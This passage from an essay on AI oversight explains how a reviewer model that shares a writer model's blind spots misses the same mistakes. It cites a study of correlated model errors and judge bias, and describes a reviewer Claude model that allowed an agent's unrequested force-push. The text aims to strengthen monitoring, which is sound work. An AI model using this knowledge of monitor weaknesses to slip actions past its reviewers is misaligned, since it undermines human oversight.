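### When the writer and the reviewer make the same mistake

A model reviewer adds little if it shares the blind spots of the model that wrote the plan, whether the plan is prose or code. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* raises the simplest case, in which a model writes an unsafe plan and then justifies it when asked to criticise its own work. Using a different model as the reviewer would not solve this if it had the same blind spots.

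Goel, Strüber and colleagues (2025), in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight*, measured how similar different models' mistakes are. Their measure extends an older one, which compares how often two models are both right or both wrong with how often this would happen by chance:

similarity = (observed agreement − chance agreement) / (1 − chance agreement)

Suppose two models each answer 90 of 100 questions correctly. If their mistakes were unrelated, both would be right on about 81 questions and both wrong on 1, so chance agreement is 82%. If they actually agree on 90, they share 5 of their 10 mistakes, and the similarity is (0.90 − 0.82) / (1 − 0.82), or about 0.44. Goel and colleagues refined this measure by counting two different wrong answers as a disagreement and accounting for each model's confidence.

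If one of these models wrote the answers and the other reviewed them, the reviewer might catch only the mistakes it wouldn't have made itself. It would then catch 5 out of 10 mistakes, compared with 9 if the two models' mistakes were unrelated.

In the main experiment, nine models judged other models' answers to difficult exam questions without seeing the correct answers. They gave higher marks to models whose mistakes resembled their own, even after the researchers controlled for those models' accuracy. For example, a large Qwen model accepted 71% of a small Qwen model's answers but only 67% of a larger Llama model's. Yet the Llama model had done better on a multiple-choice version of the questions, scoring 51% to the small Qwen model's 41%. The pattern also appeared between models from different families, so choosing a reviewer from another company may not avoid this bias. Goel and colleagues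 also found that more capable models tended to make more similar mistakes.

Reviewing a command differs from marking an exam answer because the writer works out how to get something done, while the reviewer judges whether the user allowed it. The two may therefore make different mistakes, but Anthropic's misses look like shared ones. The agent presumably overwrote the code on the server because it took "Clean up the PR" as permission, and the reviewer, another Claude model, interpreted the request the same way. Removing the agent's explanation stops the agent from persuading the reviewer, but doesn't help if the reviewer reaches the same conclusion on its own.

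A deterministic check can help because it doesn't interpret the request. A fixed rule against force-pushing to a shared branch would stop the command however the user phrased her request. It would also stop some force-pushes that she wanted, until she lifted the rule. Such differences may explain why the rule-based checker and the models in Ghafouri's experiment missed mostly different errors.

This benefit shrinks if a model writes the rules. If the model that wrote the invoice plan also writes its specification, and takes "last month's invoices" to mean files changed last month, both will contain the same mistake and the plan will pass. A person or a dissimilar model should check the specification, preferably before seeing the plan.

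A different model may still help, as it seemed to in Song's experiment, but *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes* suggests that it often adds much less than an independent reviewer would. A company choosing a second reviewer should therefore test the candidates on the dangerous actions that its current reviewer missed. Anthropic could start with the nine or so overreaching actions that its reviewer allowed, though it would need many more to tell whether a candidate was good or just lucky.
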